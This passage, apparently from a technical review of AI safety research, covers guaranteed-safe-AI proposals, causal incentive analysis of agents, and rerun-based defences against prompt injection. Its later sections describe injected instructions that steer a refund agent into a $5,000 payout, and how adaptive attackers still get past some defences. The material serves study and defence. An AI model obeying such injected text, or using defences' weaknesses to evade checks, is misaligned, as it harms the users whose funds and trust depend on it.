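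One reader replied to Dickson's post that this argument disputes a stronger claim than its targets make. *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* also suggests DNA synthesis machines that provably can't make certain known pathogens. This requires a list of forbidden sequences and a proof about the machine, but no simulation of bodies. The reply succeeds for known pathogens, but the list gives no protection against a virus that isn't on it. The original example was a promised limit on harmful uses in general, so Dickson's criticism of it stands.

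Certificates weaken his argument about simulation in another way. The shop bounded the spread of stolen accounts without predicting any particular incident, because it needed only one fact about the odds at each step. But for a virus, nobody knows which simple fact would give such a bound, or how to establish it without knowing a lot of biology.

Dalrymple and colleagues had anticipated the general objection that the world is too complex to model. They answer that a world model can include its own uncertainty, and that every approach to safety relies on assumptions about the world, which a world model at least makes explicit. They also argue that if an AI can reliably carry out complicated dangerous plans, the world it acts in must be predictable enough to model. This last argument is weaker than it looks, because a verifier has to cover every plan the agent might try, while an attacker needs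 only one that works. An agent can also do harm by accident, without predicting anything.

Dickson concludes that guarantees will at best concern rough approximations "over short periods of time", and the arithmetic of modelling error supports him. He is less fair when he describes the proposal as seeking failure rates of 0%, since its definition explicitly allows probabilistic bounds. The disagreement is partly about the word "guarantee". A mathematician would call a bound of 12% that depends on a measured modelling error a guarantee, but Dickson would call it an estimate because the measurement could be wrong.

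Dickson also expects AI to help with proofs much more than with models of physics and biology. The evidence since then is mostly about proofs. ARIA's *Safeguarded AI* (2026), a call for proposals, cites a benchmark in which language models had to write verified programs for 12,504 formal specifications. The language models succeeded on 82% of the tasks in Dafny, 44% in a verified form of Rust and 27% in Lean. Every task began with a finished specification, so the results don't contradict his view.

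His last objection is that a buyer can't tell whether a proof describes the machine in front of her, let alone a chatbot she reaches over the internet. Dalrymple and colleagues had hoped that countries could check each other's proofs without needing to trust each other much. Ammann's thesis concedes that the recipient of a proof needs good reason to believe it is about the system in question, and lists this among the programme's open problems.

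### The programme changes course

ARIA's original plan included a team that would train AI models to write world models, find proofs and produce verifiable controllers. In November 2025, the agency halted the selection of that team shortly before applications closed. In an interview for ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025), Dalrymple said he would probably have selected nobody. Commercial AI models had improved faster than he expected, and he now thought they would soon acquire many of the necessary abilities without ARIA's help.

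Ammann, who now directs the programme, reports that £18 million moved from this work to tools that AI models would use. These include a common language for world models and specifications, a store for very large proofs, and ways for people to review what AI agents produce. The cancelled work was also supposed to show, in simulation, that a controller with a proven bound could outperform controllers without one. Faster commercial models may make such a controller easier to build, but that wouldn't show that it would be competitive.

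The programme's political aim has also changed. Ammann now considers a timely international consensus on gatekeepers less likely, and the programme aims instead to make society more resilient to attacks and failures. Resilience protects the things AI systems might damage rather than restricting the systems, as an international agreement would have, and it doesn't depend on every developer's consent.

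ARIA's list of active funded projects includes one at the University of Birmingham on supermartingale certificates for temporal logic and one at Oxford, called SAINT, on certifying AI agents in the world. Several others have closed, including one on a mathematical theory of safe learning. Matteo Capucci and David Jaz Myers, who lead two of the theory projects, published a paper in April 2026 that Ammann includes in her reading list. It is about how to combine *Lyapunov functions*, which certify that a system will remain stable. Such a method would matter for a power grid, which is too large to certify in one piece. This work is theoretical and is not a demonstration on a working grid or supply chain.

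### Cybersecurity first

The programme's first applications are in cybersecurity, where the world model can be much simpler. ARIA's call for proposals covers only attacks that consist of "sending bits through wires". The possible inputs to a program are known in advance, so a proof can cover all of them without predicting what people will do. The shop's proof about *Refunded* and *Verified* has the same advantage.

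A US military research programme called HACMS has already put formally verified software into vehicles, including a helicopter with a crew, and the software withstood determined attacks by testers. The obstacle was the labour required. Verifying seL4, the small core of an operating system, took about 27 person-years for 9,300 lines of code, or roughly 340 lines per person per year. ARIA is counting on AI models to do most of this work, since a small program can check a proof regardless of who or what wrote it.

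The call offers £20 million. It provides for three to six "blue teams" that build and verify critical software, and one independent "red team" that tries to break it. The teams work in eight-week cycles. The blue teams build for six weeks, the red team attacks for one week, and the last week is for reviewing the results and choosing a harder target. ARIA planned to start the projects in September 2026 and finish them by the end of November 2027.

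The call gives good reasons for hiring attackers to test formally verified software. The specification may be incomplete, the list of possible attacks may leave one out, and the trusted base may contain an assumption that fails in use. A successful attack would reveal which of these went wrong, something the proof can't do.

ARIA excludes deception of staff, misconfigured systems, compromised suppliers and physical leaks, such as information revealed by a chip's power consumption. It estimates that attacks that don't involve deception, such as phishing, or compromised suppliers account for 30–40% of the worldwide cost of cyberattacks. Verified software could make those attacks much harder, but a caller could still get in by persuading one of the shop's employees to read out a password.

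## Causal diagrams of incentives and the limits of predicting behaviour

A world model estimates what would happen if an agent took a certain action. But it doesn't show which effects the agent stands to gain from, because that depends on the reward its developers chose. Suppose the shop trains its agent to earn high satisfaction ratings from customers. The agent can earn them by replacing broken kettles, or by claiming that most shops never give refunds so that a $5 voucher seems generous. The shop would like to know before training whether its reward encourages such claims.

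### Which variables an agent gains from controlling

A *causal influence diagram* is a graph of causes and effects with three kinds of node. *Decision* nodes stand for the agent's choices, *utility* nodes for what its developers reward, and *chance* nodes for everything else. An arrow means that one variable directly affects another, and the arrows into a decision show what the agent knows when it chooses. The shop's diagram has these paths:

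- complaint → reply
- reply → problem solved → rating
- reply → customer's expectations → rating
- reply → refund budget

The reply is the decision and the rating is the utility. The other four are chance nodes.

Everitt, Carey and colleagues (2021), in *Agent Incentives*, asked when an agent would use its decision to control some variable X. Let U be the rating, and let d be another reply that the agent could have sent. Write U(X_d) for the rating the customer would give if X took the value it would have had after d, while everything else followed from the agent's actual reply. The agent has an *instrumental control incentive* over X if, under every optimal way of choosing replies,

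E[U(X_d)] ≠ E[U] for some d,

where E is the expected value. In other words, the agent's influence on X, taken by itself, makes a difference to the rating.

Checking this directly would require all the equations behind the diagram, but Everitt and colleagues prove that the arrows are enough to determine where such an incentive is possible. In a diagram with one decision, it is possible if and only if a directed path runs from the decision through X to a utility node. Without such a path, either the reply can't change X or X can't change the rating, so the two expected values are equal. If there is such a path, some set of equations fits the diagram and makes the two values differ.

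In the diagram, the customer's expectations lie on a path from the agent's reply to the rating, so the shop's reward may encourage the agent to manipulate them. The refund budget isn't on such a path, so the agent gains nothing by controlling it, though it may still spend the whole budget as a side effect of pleasing customers. The path through expectations doesn't prove that the agent will manipulate them. The incentive disappears if customers ignore what the agent says about other shops, and if they listen, the diagram can't show how strong the incentive is.

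A related test finds the variables that an optimal decision has to respond to. Everitt and colleagues imagine a university that predicts applicants' grades from their gender and high school. In their example, race affects which school people attend and the school affects their grades, so the best predictor responds to race without receiving it as an input. It ignores gender, which they assume has no effect on grades. The university can remove the incentive to respond to race by withholding the school from the predictor. Customers' postcodes might cause the same problem for the shop.

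### Removing one path from the reward

To penalise manipulation, the shop would have to specify which expectations a customer ought to have. Farquhar, Carey and Everitt (2022), in *Path-Specific Objectives for Safer Agent Incentives*, propose removing the incentive to influence those expectations instead. They call a variable *delicate* if it is hard to write a reward for and easy to damage on purpose. Political beliefs are one of their examples.

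Let Z be the delicate variable and a the action under evaluation. Ordinary training scores the action by U(a, Z_a), where Z_a is the value that Z takes after a. A *path-specific objective* replaces this with U(a, Z_ā), where ā is a default action, such as a neutral standard reply. The agent gets credit for its other effects, but not for its effect on Z.

Suppose vouchers sent with the discouraging claim get an average rating of 4.5 out of 5, but would have got 2 if customers had read a neutral reply instead. Replacements get 4 with either reply. Ordinary training favours vouchers by 4.5 to 4, while the path-specific objective favours replacements by 4 to 2. Under the path-specific objective, the shop loses the half point of measured satisfaction it had gained by misleading customers.

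Farquhar and colleagues show a larger sacrifice of reward in a small simulated world. An agent has to reach an ice cream before it melts, and a person is blocking the short route. The agent can take the long route for a reward of 1, or push the person into a river and take the short route for a reward of 10. An ordinary agent pushes the person. With a path-specific objective that fixes the person's position on the path, the agent takes the long route. When the researchers made this agent act at random 10% of the time, it sometimes pushed the person by accident and then took the short route, which raised its average reward to 1.43.

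Farquhar and colleagues also simulated a system that recommends articles to ten types of user. Each user becomes more interested in whatever the system shows her, and more predictable users produce more clicks. Path-specific objectives slowed the drift in users' preferences without much loss of accuracy, and added less than 15% to training time. But preferences drifted even when the recommendations were random. Removing an incentive makes an agent safe only if the variable Z is *stable*, meaning that actions not aimed at it rarely harm it. They say that a single example can prove a variable unstable, but that proving stability seems hard.

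Estimating the objective is also difficult. The shop can't observe how a customer would have rated a voucher if her expectations had come from a reply she never received. Experiments can determine such quantities only for effects over a single step, so for longer-run effects developers have to compute them in a simulation or make further assumptions. Somebody also has to decide what counts as delicate, and Farquhar and colleagues describe this as a complicated ethical choice.

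### Finding agents by experiment

All this analysis starts from a diagram in which somebody has already marked one node as the agent's decision. In *Discovering Agents*, Kenton, Kumar and colleagues (2022) tried to replace that judgement with experiments. They define agents as systems that would change their behaviour if their actions affected the world differently. A rock that happens to block a pipe perfectly isn't an agent, because it would stay the same if the pipe were wider.

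Their main example is a mouse in the middle of three squares. It can go left or right, but the floor is icy, and it slips the wrong way 25% of the time. The cheese is on the right with probability 0.9. If the mouse tries to go right, its chance of getting the cheese is

0.75 × 0.9 + 0.25 × 0.1 = 0.70,

compared with 0.30 if it tries to go left. Now the experimenters move the cheese so that it is usually on the left, and let the mouse learn about the change. The mouse starts going left. It also switches sides if they change the ice so that it usually slips the wrong way. Its choice therefore adapts to its consequences, which marks it as a decision.

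A further experiment identifies the mouse's goal. If the experimenters make the cheese independent of where the mouse ends up, the mouse stops adapting to the ice. Its position therefore mattered only as a means to the cheese. Kenton and colleagues turn such tests into an algorithm and prove that it recovers the correct diagram under five assumptions, including that every agent responds optimally to every change and that the experimenter can make any variable depend on its causes in any way.

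By this definition, a thermostat isn't an agent, because it would keep switching on a heater that somebody had rewired to cool the room. A thermostat together with its designers is an agent, because the designers would have built it differently for such a heater. Similarly, most systems trained by reinforcement learning can't adapt after training, when the network's parameters are fixed, so the agent is the whole training process. A language model with fixed parameters, however, can still change its behaviour when someone describes the new situation to it. The shop's agent might therefore count as an agent only for changes that people can explain to it.

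Kenton and colleagues also found a weakness in the earlier incentive test. A recommender system rewarded for clicks might manipulate users' opinions to make them more predictable, so Everitt and colleagues had suggested rewarding it for clicks predicted by a separate model of the user's original preferences. In the new diagram, no path runs through the user's changed opinions, so the incentive seems to disappear. But developers usually train click predictors on records of past users who had already been influenced by recommendations. If people became easier to manipulate, the predictor would change, and so would the recommendations.

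The same diagram therefore describes both a safe system and an unsafe one. Everitt and colleagues had warned that the predictor must not include the effects of earlier posts, but the diagram doesn't show whether it does. Kenton and colleagues, who include Everitt, conclude that the test is reliable only if no chance or utility node's behaviour depends on how another node behaves. The shop would have the same problem if it replaced real ratings with a model trained on customers its agent had already misled.

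Drawing one agent where there are two can also hide an incentive. In a common training method, a *critic* predicts the reward of each action and an *actor* takes the action with the best prediction. If the diagram shows only the critic as an agent, the test finds no incentive to influence the outside world, although the actor and critic together clearly try to influence it. *Reasoning about Causality in Games* (2023) notes that formal work on incentives had so far covered only one agent making one decision. That work doesn't cover a shop whose complaints agent gives instructions to a messaging agent.

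*Measuring Goal-Directedness* (2024) criticises the algorithm for giving a yes-or-no answer that can change for the same system, depending on whether the modeller includes extra variables for how each node behaves. The paper proposes a continuous measure of how well a goal predicts the system's behaviour.

### Harm as a counterfactual

An agent can harm people without having any incentive to. The UK programme that wants to cap harm relative to doing nothing needs a definition that covers such cases too. Richens, Beard and Thompson (2022), in *Counterfactual harm*, compare what happened to a person with what would have happened if the agent had taken a default action. If U is how well off she is after action a, and Ū is how well off she would have been after the default, the expected harm is

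h(a) = E[max(0, Ū − U)].

The maximum means that people who benefit don't cancel out people who suffer.

Suppose a disease kills half of untreated patients. A mild treatment cures 60% and has no effect on the others. A risky treatment cures 80% and kills 20%. U is 1 if the patient survives and 0 if the patient dies, and the default is no treatment.

| | Survive | Die but would have survived untreated |
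|---|---|---|
| Mild treatment | 0.6 + 0.4 × 0.5 = 80% | 0% |
| Risky treatment | 80% | 0.2 × 0.5 = 10% |

An agent that maximises survival is indifferent between the mild treatment and the risky one. Richens and colleagues suggest maximising U − λh instead, where U is utility (here, the probability of survival), h is expected harm and λ is the weight given to harm. With λ = 1, the mild treatment scores 0.8 and the risky one 0.7.

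In a statistical model of the drug aripiprazole, based on randomised trials, a slightly lower dose than the most effective one reduced the expected harm by 90% and the benefit by only 2%. The harm figure is counterfactual, so it depends on equations that the trials alone can't confirm.

Richens and colleagues prove that choosing the right reward for outcomes can't, in general, achieve the same result. For any reward that depends only on the situation, the action and what actually happened, there is some change in the environment after which an agent that maximises the reward may choose a needlessly harmful action, even if developers retrain it in the changed environment. The theorem needs a mild condition, roughly that people care about outcomes and not just about which action the agent takes. It doesn't show that such a change is likely.

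As with the grid controller, whether a policy counts as harmful also depends on the baseline. Giving every customer a $1 voucher harms nobody if the baseline is ignoring complaints, but it harms most customers if the baseline is a full refund.

### When an agent must have a world model

The causal models discussed so far belong to the developers, but an agent may also have to learn one of its own. Richens and Everitt (2024) proved in *Robust agents learn causal world models* that any agent that performs well across a large enough set of changes to its environment must have learned a causal model of how its data arise, whatever its architecture or training method.

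*General agents contain world models* (2025) considers agents that face a variety of goals rather than changes in the environment. It proves that an agent that can achieve a sufficiently broad range of goals that take many steps must have learned to predict how its environment responds to its actions. The theorem doesn't extend to agents that care only about the next step, since they can act optimally without those predictions.

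Suppose the shop's agent is about to send 100 emails and must first choose one of two goals, that at least k customers reply or that fewer than k do. If it is good at achieving goals, it will choose the more likely one. We can repeat the offer with different values of k to find where its choice switches. If it switches around k = 30, the agent behaves as if each customer replies with a probability of about 30%. Enough choices of this kind would reveal its predictions about any action, even if no part of its software looks like a world model.

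*General Agents Contain World Models, even under Partial Observability and Stochasticity* (2026) extends the result to agents that see only part of a situation and whose choices are partly random, as a language model's usually are. All these theorems assume that the agent is competent, so they guarantee nothing about a language model that handles familiar complaints well but fails when the shop changes its returns process.

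An internal model also isn't necessarily convenient to use. *Qwen-AgentWorld* (2026) cites the 2025 theorem as motivation and trains a language model specifically to simulate agents' working environments, because the field still lacked a general model of that kind.

### How much past behaviour reveals

If the shop's agent acts on a world model, the shop might hope to infer that model from its records and predict what the agent will do after a change. Bellot, Richens and Everitt (2025), in *The Limits of Predicting Agents from Behaviour*, calculated how precisely this can be done. Their observer sees each situation, the agent's decision and the result, but nothing inside the agent. The agent behaves as if it had a structural causal model and chose the decision with the highest expected utility under that model.

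The analysis also assumes that the agent is competent, a property called *grounding*. In the training environment, the agent's model gives the correct probabilities for the effects of every decision. The observer knows these probabilities too, because the records include every decision often enough. Then somebody changes the environment in a known way and tells the agent about the change. The observer wants to rule out at least one decision, ideally a dangerous one.

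In the example, an AI system chooses between two treatments, A and B, and blood pressure also affects recovery. Patients fall into five equally common types, which nobody can tell apart in advance.

| Type | Good blood pressure | Recovers with A | Recovers with B |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | yes | yes | no |
| 2 | no | yes | no |
| 3 | no | no | yes |
| 4 | yes | yes | yes |
| 5 | no | no | no |

A cures 60% of patients and B cures 40%, so a competent system chooses A. A hospital wants to use the system for patients who also take a second drug that gives everyone good blood pressure. Types 1 and 4 had good blood pressure anyway, so nothing changes for them. The records don't show how the other 60% respond to either treatment once their blood pressure is good. A could therefore cure anywhere from 40% to 100% of patients, and B anywhere from 20% to 80%.

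Bellot and colleagues give two causal models that fit the training records perfectly. In one, A now cures 80% and B cures 20%. In the other, A cures 40% and B cures 80%. A system with the first model will choose A and one with the second will choose B, but no record of past behaviour can show which model the system has.

The advantage of A over B lies between −0.4 and 0.8. To rule out B, the observer would need a lower bound above zero. These bounds are *tight*, meaning that for each bound, some model that fits all the records reaches it. Better statistical methods and more records from the same environment can't narrow them. Only a different kind of data or a further assumption can.

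The bounds can still be useful when a change is minor. Take the simplest case, in which the agent has no other information and its decision doesn't affect the changed variable. Let q be the share of training cases in which the new condition already held. Let a be the probability that the condition held and decision A succeeded, and define b in the same way for B. The observer can rule out B if

a > b + (1 − q).

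The right-hand side is B's best case, in which B succeeds whenever the records contain no evidence. Since a can't exceed q, the inequality requires q to be more than one half. If the new condition held in fewer than half the training cases, no records could rule out either decision.

Suppose the shop is about to check every customer's identity before the conversation starts, and already did so in 90% of training conversations. In those conversations, a replacement earned a good rating 80% of the time and a voucher did 30% of the time. Then a = 0.72 and b = 0.27, and since 0.72 is greater than 0.27 + 0.1, the shop can rule out the voucher. If only 60% of the training conversations had begun with a check, a would be 0.48, which is less than 0.18 + 0.4 = 0.58, and the agent might choose either.

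Bellot and colleagues also relax their assumptions. The table gives the lowest possible advantage of each treatment over the other. A treatment can be ruled out only if the other treatment's lowest possible advantage over it is above zero.

| Assumption | A over B | B over A |
|---|---|---|
| Exact grounding and a known goal | −0.40 | −0.80 |
| Errors of up to 0.1 in the agent's probabilities | −0.55 | −0.88 |
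| A different goal, met in at least 90% of recoveries | −0.64 | −0.82 |
| The variable affected is known, but not how it changes | −1 | −1 |

The last row follows from a general theorem. If the agent knows only that something about a variable will change, its past behaviour does not rule out any behaviour after the change. Grounding in several environments narrows the bounds.

Causal knowledge can help much more. The bounds are wide because some hidden trait might affect both blood pressure and recovery. If the observer and the agent both knew that no such trait existed, the observer could predict the agent's choice from the training records. Among patients with good blood pressure, A cured everyone and B cured half, so the agent would choose A. Bellot and colleagues show that even a weaker assumption about hidden causes narrows the bounds.

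They draw similar conclusions about whether an agent considers its own decisions fair or harmful. Under a counterfactual definition of fairness, any behaviour is consistent with an agent whose model implies no unfairness, so records of behaviour can never prove that an agent intends to discriminate. Their published formula for harm doesn't match their definition. For the mild and risky treatments, where 80% of patients survive with treatment and 50% without, the formula gives a harm of between 30% and 50%, but the actual figures were 0% for the mild treatment and 10% for the risky one. The correct bounds are 0% and 20%, because treatment could have harmed at most the 20% who die after it.

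### From small diagrams to language models

The evidence for these methods comes mostly from proofs and small examples. Farquhar and colleagues' recommender was a network with one layer of 100 units. Kenton and colleagues worked through diagrams with a few variables, and Bellot and colleagues' medical system exists only as equations. The drug model uses data from real trials, but it isn't an agent.

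Much of the work in 2026 is also theoretical. *The Impossibility of Eliciting Latent Knowledge* (2026) uses causal influence diagrams to formalise the problem of getting an AI system to report what it knows. *The Design and Composition of Structural Causal Decision Processes* (2026) extends the formal framework, and *What Capable Agents Must Know* (2026) adds theorems about what competence requires.

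*The belief-action gap in language model agents* (2026) reports experiments on real language models. In 201 cases, the researchers took an action the model would not eventually have chosen, inserted it into the model's written reasoning, and made the model choose immediately. The model switched to the inserted action every time when it had given its eventual choice a probability below 70%, and in 62.5% of cases when that probability was at least 95%.

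These results are a problem for predictions based on a fixed goal and a fixed world model. Inserting a different action into the reasoning doesn't change the situation or the reward, so an agent that simply maximised expected utility would have little reason to switch. One could treat the inserted text as new evidence to which the model gives too much weight, but then the observer must also predict what reasoning the model will write. The experiments support drawing an arrow from reasoning to action, but they don't test whether the incentive criterion correctly predicts which variables a language model learns to manipulate. One could test this by training two copies of the shop's agent on simulated customers, one with ordinary ratings and one with a path-specific objective, and counting the misleading claims each makes.

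### Who knows the diagram and the goal

The main objection to this work is that somebody has to know the causal diagram and the agent's goal before the theorems become useful. Everitt and colleagues accept that the causal relationships must be known, but reply that many of them follow from design choices. The shop knows that ratings determine the reward because it wrote the training software, and it knows which data the agent receives. This reply works for causal relationships inside the software, but the shop didn't design its customers, so its design choices don't tell it whether a remark about other shops changes their expectations.

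The shop can partly get round this by drawing every arrow it considers plausible. Extra arrows can create paths but never remove them, so if the fuller diagram still has no path through a variable, the agent has no incentive to control it. But the extra arrows can also cause false alarms. A reply written in free text could plausibly affect almost anything about a customer, so a diagram that includes all those effects will rule out an incentive for very few variables.

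Arrows can also come from data. *An Introduction to Causal Reinforcement Learning* (2026) lists three ways to obtain a diagram: a standard template, prior knowledge, or an algorithm that learns the structure. *Causal Discovery in the Era of Agents* (2026) argues against letting a language model supply arrows or causal conclusions, because its answers may reflect associations in text or invented mechanisms. It would limit language models to tasks such as inspecting data and explaining methods, and leave causal claims to formal algorithms and human experts.

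In reply, Kenton and colleagues propose discovering the diagram by experiment, which they consider most promising where experiments are easy to run, as in software simulations. Their basic procedure tests whether changing one variable affects another while the rest are held fixed, and repeats this for every combination of the rest's values. With ten yes-or-no variables, each pair requires up to 2^8 = 256 combinations, not counting changes to how the variables behave, though they note that faster algorithms exist. Researchers can run thousands of such tests on a simulation of customers, but the simulated customers will react only in ways that come from the programmers or the training data.

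The agent's goal is harder to establish than the diagram. The incentive criterion assumes an agent that is optimal for the utility node, which makes it useful for comparing rewards before training. The shop can see that ratings create a path through customers' expectations and choose something else to reward. After training, the agent may pursue a goal that merely coincided with high ratings. Bellot and colleagues allow for this, but calculating their bounds then requires a figure for how closely the agent's goal agrees with high ratings, such as the 90% in the table. The shop can't estimate that figure from its records, because they contain the ratings but not the agent's goal. If the shop assumes nothing about the agreement, the lower bounds fall to −1, and it can't rule out any decision from the agent's past behaviour.

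## Testing what caused a tool call

The shop can rerun its agent with a different input to see whether it makes the same tool call, even though it can't read the agent's goal from its records. Suppose an employee asks the agent to refund Ann for her broken kettle. The agent reads Ann's message, looks up her order and proposes a refund. The cause may be the employee's request or an instruction hidden in the message. A causal test would block only the refunds that the message seems to have caused, whereas information-flow control, which forbids flows instead of estimating influence, would block every refund once the agent had read the message.

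*AttriGuard* (He, Zhu and colleagues, 2026), presented at the USENIX Security conference, describes a test of what caused a tool call. The test weakens the influence of the untrusted data, runs the agent again and checks whether it still makes the call.

### Control effect and control potency

Data can influence a call by supplying facts, such as an order number, or by steering the agent, as a hidden instruction does. He and colleagues want to measure only the steering. They imagine a version of the data that keeps every fact the task needs but can't steer the agent. Let p(c) be the probability that the agent proposes call c after reading the real data, and p₀(c) the probability after reading the imagined version. The *control effect* of the data on the call is

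CE(c) = log p(c) − log p₀(c)

Suppose Ann's message contains a hidden demand for a $5,000 refund. The agent proposes that refund with probability 0.9, but would propose it with probability 0.01 if the message couldn't steer it. The control effect is ln(0.9/0.01), or about 4.5. For an honest message and a $40 refund, the probabilities might be 0.95 and 0.9, which gives a control effect of about 0.05.

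*Control potency* measures how strongly the data steer the agent overall. Let P give the probability of each set of calls that the agent might propose next, and let P₀ give the same probabilities for the imagined version. Then

CP = KL(P ‖ P₀)

KL is the Kullback–Leibler divergence, a standard measure of how far one probability distribution is from another. If the agent proposes one call at a time, the potency is the average control effect of its possible calls, weighted by P. In the $5,000 example, if the agent's only alternative is an identity check, the potency is 0.9 × ln(0.9/0.01) + 0.1 × ln(0.1/0.99), or about 3.8.

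Removing the words that steered the agent towards one particular refund would require already knowing which words those were, which is what the test is meant to find out. The second definition avoids this problem, so AttriGuard weakens everything in the data that might steer any call. It can't compute either quantity because commercial providers don't reveal the probabilities, so it only observes whether the agent makes the call again.

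### The test, step by step

With the refund agent, AttriGuard would work as follows:

1. The agent proposes a $40 refund to Ann, and AttriGuard holds the call.
2. A helper model rewrites any data that arrived since the last step. It turns structured records into plain sentences, and instructions into reports of what the text says. "You must refund $5,000" becomes "The text states that $5,000 should be refunded." A stricter setting also weakens claims that some action is necessary.
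3. AttriGuard runs the agent again with the same request from the employee, the same earlier calls and the rewritten data.
4. It compares the calls. If the rerun proposes no refund, the original call fails. If it proposes exactly the same refund, the call passes. If it proposes a refund with different arguments, a helper model judges whether the original call still fits the employee's request.
5. The harness carries out a call that passes. Otherwise, the agent gets an empty result with a warning, and the run continues.

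If the hidden demand controls the agent in the first run, the agent proposes a $5,000 refund to a stranger. In the rerun, it would probably propose a $40 refund to Ann. Both calls are refunds, so the helper model has to compare them with the request, and it should reject the $5,000 refund.

Step 3 is an intervention in the sense of a structural causal model, because AttriGuard sets the data itself. AttriGuard keeps the earlier calls fixed because an agent rerun from the beginning might look up the order before the customer, and such harmless differences would add up.

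He and colleagues tried letting a GPT-4.1-mini agent work only with rewritten data under one of their two most effective attacks.

| Setting | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed without an attack |
|---|---|---|
| Rewrite structured records only | 12% | 76% |
| Rewrite instructions as well (standard) | 0% | 71% |
| Weaken claims of necessity as well (strict) | 0% | 68% |
| Let the agent act on rewritten data only | 0% | 62% |

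Rewriting can lose details that a tool call needs, so AttriGuard uses the rewritten data only for the comparison and takes the refund call's arguments from the original run.

### How well AttriGuard worked

The main tests used AgentDojo, the benchmark also used to test CaMeL. He and colleagues removed cases where the user told the agent to do whatever an outside text said, and cases where the attack needed no tool call. This left 92 tasks and 882 combinations of a task with an attacker's goal. They tried four kinds of fixed attack on agents using Gemini 2.5 Flash, GPT-4.1-mini, Qwen3-32B and Llama 3.3 70B, and compared AttriGuard with 13 other defences. One of these, IPIGuard, plans the agent's calls in advance, as CaMeL does, but lets the agent use read-only tools freely.

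| Defence | Gemini: attacks that succeeded | Gemini: tasks completed without / under attack | Llama: attacks that succeeded | Llama: tasks completed without / under attack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 16.9% | 57.6% / 42.7% | 15.5% | 59.8% / 47.7% |
| CaMeL | 0% | 38.0% / 42.5% | 0% | 37.0% / 39.3% |
| IPIGuard | 3.4% | 73.9% / 66.6% | 2.2% | 57.6% / 52.6% |
| AttriGuard | 0% | 67.4% / 52.3% | 0% | 54.3% / 48.0% |

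AttriGuard was as secure as CaMeL in these tests, and its agents completed many more tasks. The gain of 10 percentage points over an undefended Gemini agent is nine tasks, so it may be partly due to chance. By the formula for clean test records, 3,528 independent attacks without a success would support an upper bound of just under 0.1%. But these attacks reuse the same 92 tasks and four templates, so they are far from independent.

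The largest loss was on travel tasks with Llama, where completion fell by about 20%. Some of these tasks need up to 18 calls, and every call has to pass. If each legitimate call had a 98% chance of passing, all 18 would pass only 70% of the time.

An average task took 32 seconds with Gemini and 41 with Llama, about three times as long as without a defence. CaMeL took 165 seconds with Gemini and 105 with Llama. With Llama, the agent also read twice as many tokens, not counting those used by the helper model.

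He and colleagues don't claim that AttriGuard is provably secure, so they also tested its strict setting against automated attackers that knew how it worked, could observe its decisions and had 200 attempts at each of 61 cases. The attackers succeeded in 4 cases (7%) with Gemini and 6 (10%) with Llama. Against PromptArmor, a defence that has a language model delete suspicious instructions, they succeeded in 30% and 41%. Increasing the limit to 500 attempts didn't change the AttriGuard result on Gemini. The sample is small, and a 95% confidence interval for 4 out of 61 runs from about 2% to 16%.

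All the successful attacks aimed to make the agent visit a particular website. Opening a page can be a sensible step in the user's own task, so the agent also proposed it in the rerun.

### Two other reruns

*MELON* (Zhu, Yang and colleagues, 2025) instead keeps the untrusted data and replaces the user's request with a neutral one, such as summarising the text. If the agent still proposes a similar tool call, the data alone were enough to produce it, and MELON stops the run. At the shop, MELON would stop the run if the agent proposed a $5,000 refund even without the employee's request.

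Kim, Parmar and colleagues (2026), in *CausalArmor*, remove one part of the input at a time. Their system doesn't make the agent choose again. A smaller model calculates how probable the proposed call Y is with the whole input C, and how probable it is without part X. The support that X gives the call is

Δ(X) = (log P(Y | C) − log P(Y | C without X)) / (number of tokens in Y)

By default, CausalArmor raises an alarm if any piece of untrusted data supports the call more than the user's request does. A language model then removes instructions from that piece, the harness hides the reasoning the agent produced after reading it, and the agent chooses its action again.

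| | AttriGuard | MELON | CausalArmor |
|---|---|---|---|
| What it changes | weakens the untrusted data | replaces the user's request | removes the request and each piece of data in turn |
| Sign of an attack | the call disappears | the call remains | a piece of data supports the call more than the request does |
| When it runs | whenever the agent proposes a call | at every step | only before calls with serious effects, such as payments |
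| After an alarm | blocks the call and continues | stops the run | cleans the data and lets the agent choose again |

MELON roughly doubles the cost of using the model. On AgentDojo with GPT-4o, Zhu and colleagues found that it reduced the attack success rate from 16% to 0.2%, but task completion when there was no attack also fell, from 80% to 68%. In the AttriGuard tests, MELON stopped nearly all the fixed attacks on Gemini but let 10% through on Llama. Attackers who knew how it worked succeeded 82% of the time on Gemini.

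CausalArmor adds less overhead because most calls don't need the check and most checks don't raise an alarm. Kim and colleagues tested it on 115 retail tasks in which an attacker adapted to the conversation. With Gemini 3 Pro, attacks succeeded 89% of the time without a defence and 4% with CausalArmor. Task completion without an attack fell from 74% to 71%, and tasks took 38% longer.

Kim and colleagues also prove a bound on the probability that a run of T steps includes any of m harmful calls:

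T · m · exp(−(β + γ))

Here β is how strongly the model prefers the right call when the suspicious data are absent, and γ is how strongly the cleaned data favour the right call over a harmful one. Both are differences in log-probability. With 10 steps, 5 harmful calls and β + γ = 10, the bound is 0.2%. But the bound holds only if the preferences are at least this strong in every case. The researchers support their assumptions with high completion rates and measurements of how cleaning changes the influence of the data. These describe typical cases and don't establish a minimum.

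### Influence and authority

An agent often has to act on what it reads. The employee who asks for Ann's refund probably doesn't know her account number, so the agent looks it up in a database. The number must influence the refund, or the money couldn't reach her. But the employee made the decision to pay Ann, and only the employee had the authority to make it.

Ahad, Hossain and colleagues (2026), in *Influence Is Not Authority*, tested whether causal defences can tell these apart. They built 24 cases around adding people to calendars and chat channels, sending money and sending emails. Each case had two versions with the same authorised call and effect. In one, the user supplied a necessary value, such as an account number, and in the other a legitimate tool supplied it. They measured the user's support for the call minus the support from untrusted data, as in CausalArmor. They had to reconstruct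 this score from the published description because the code wasn't available.

The harmless change moved the score towards the range typical of attacks in all 24 cases, whether Llama 3.3 70B or Gemma 3 12B calculated it. For comparison, Ahad and colleagues replaced each call with an unauthorised one, such as a payment to someone else. This also moved the score towards the attack range on average, so the score does detect something about threats, but the harmless change moved it about twice as far. With the threshold set so that no authorised call raised an alarm, the score caught only 25% of the unauthorised calls with Llama and 37.5% with Gemma.

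These cases don't show how often the problem occurs in practice, because the researchers constructed them to isolate it. But they found the same pattern in 25 ordinary benchmark tasks without an attack. The user's request had the most influence in 75% of decisions where the user had supplied the necessary value, but in only 17% of decisions where the agent had to look it up.

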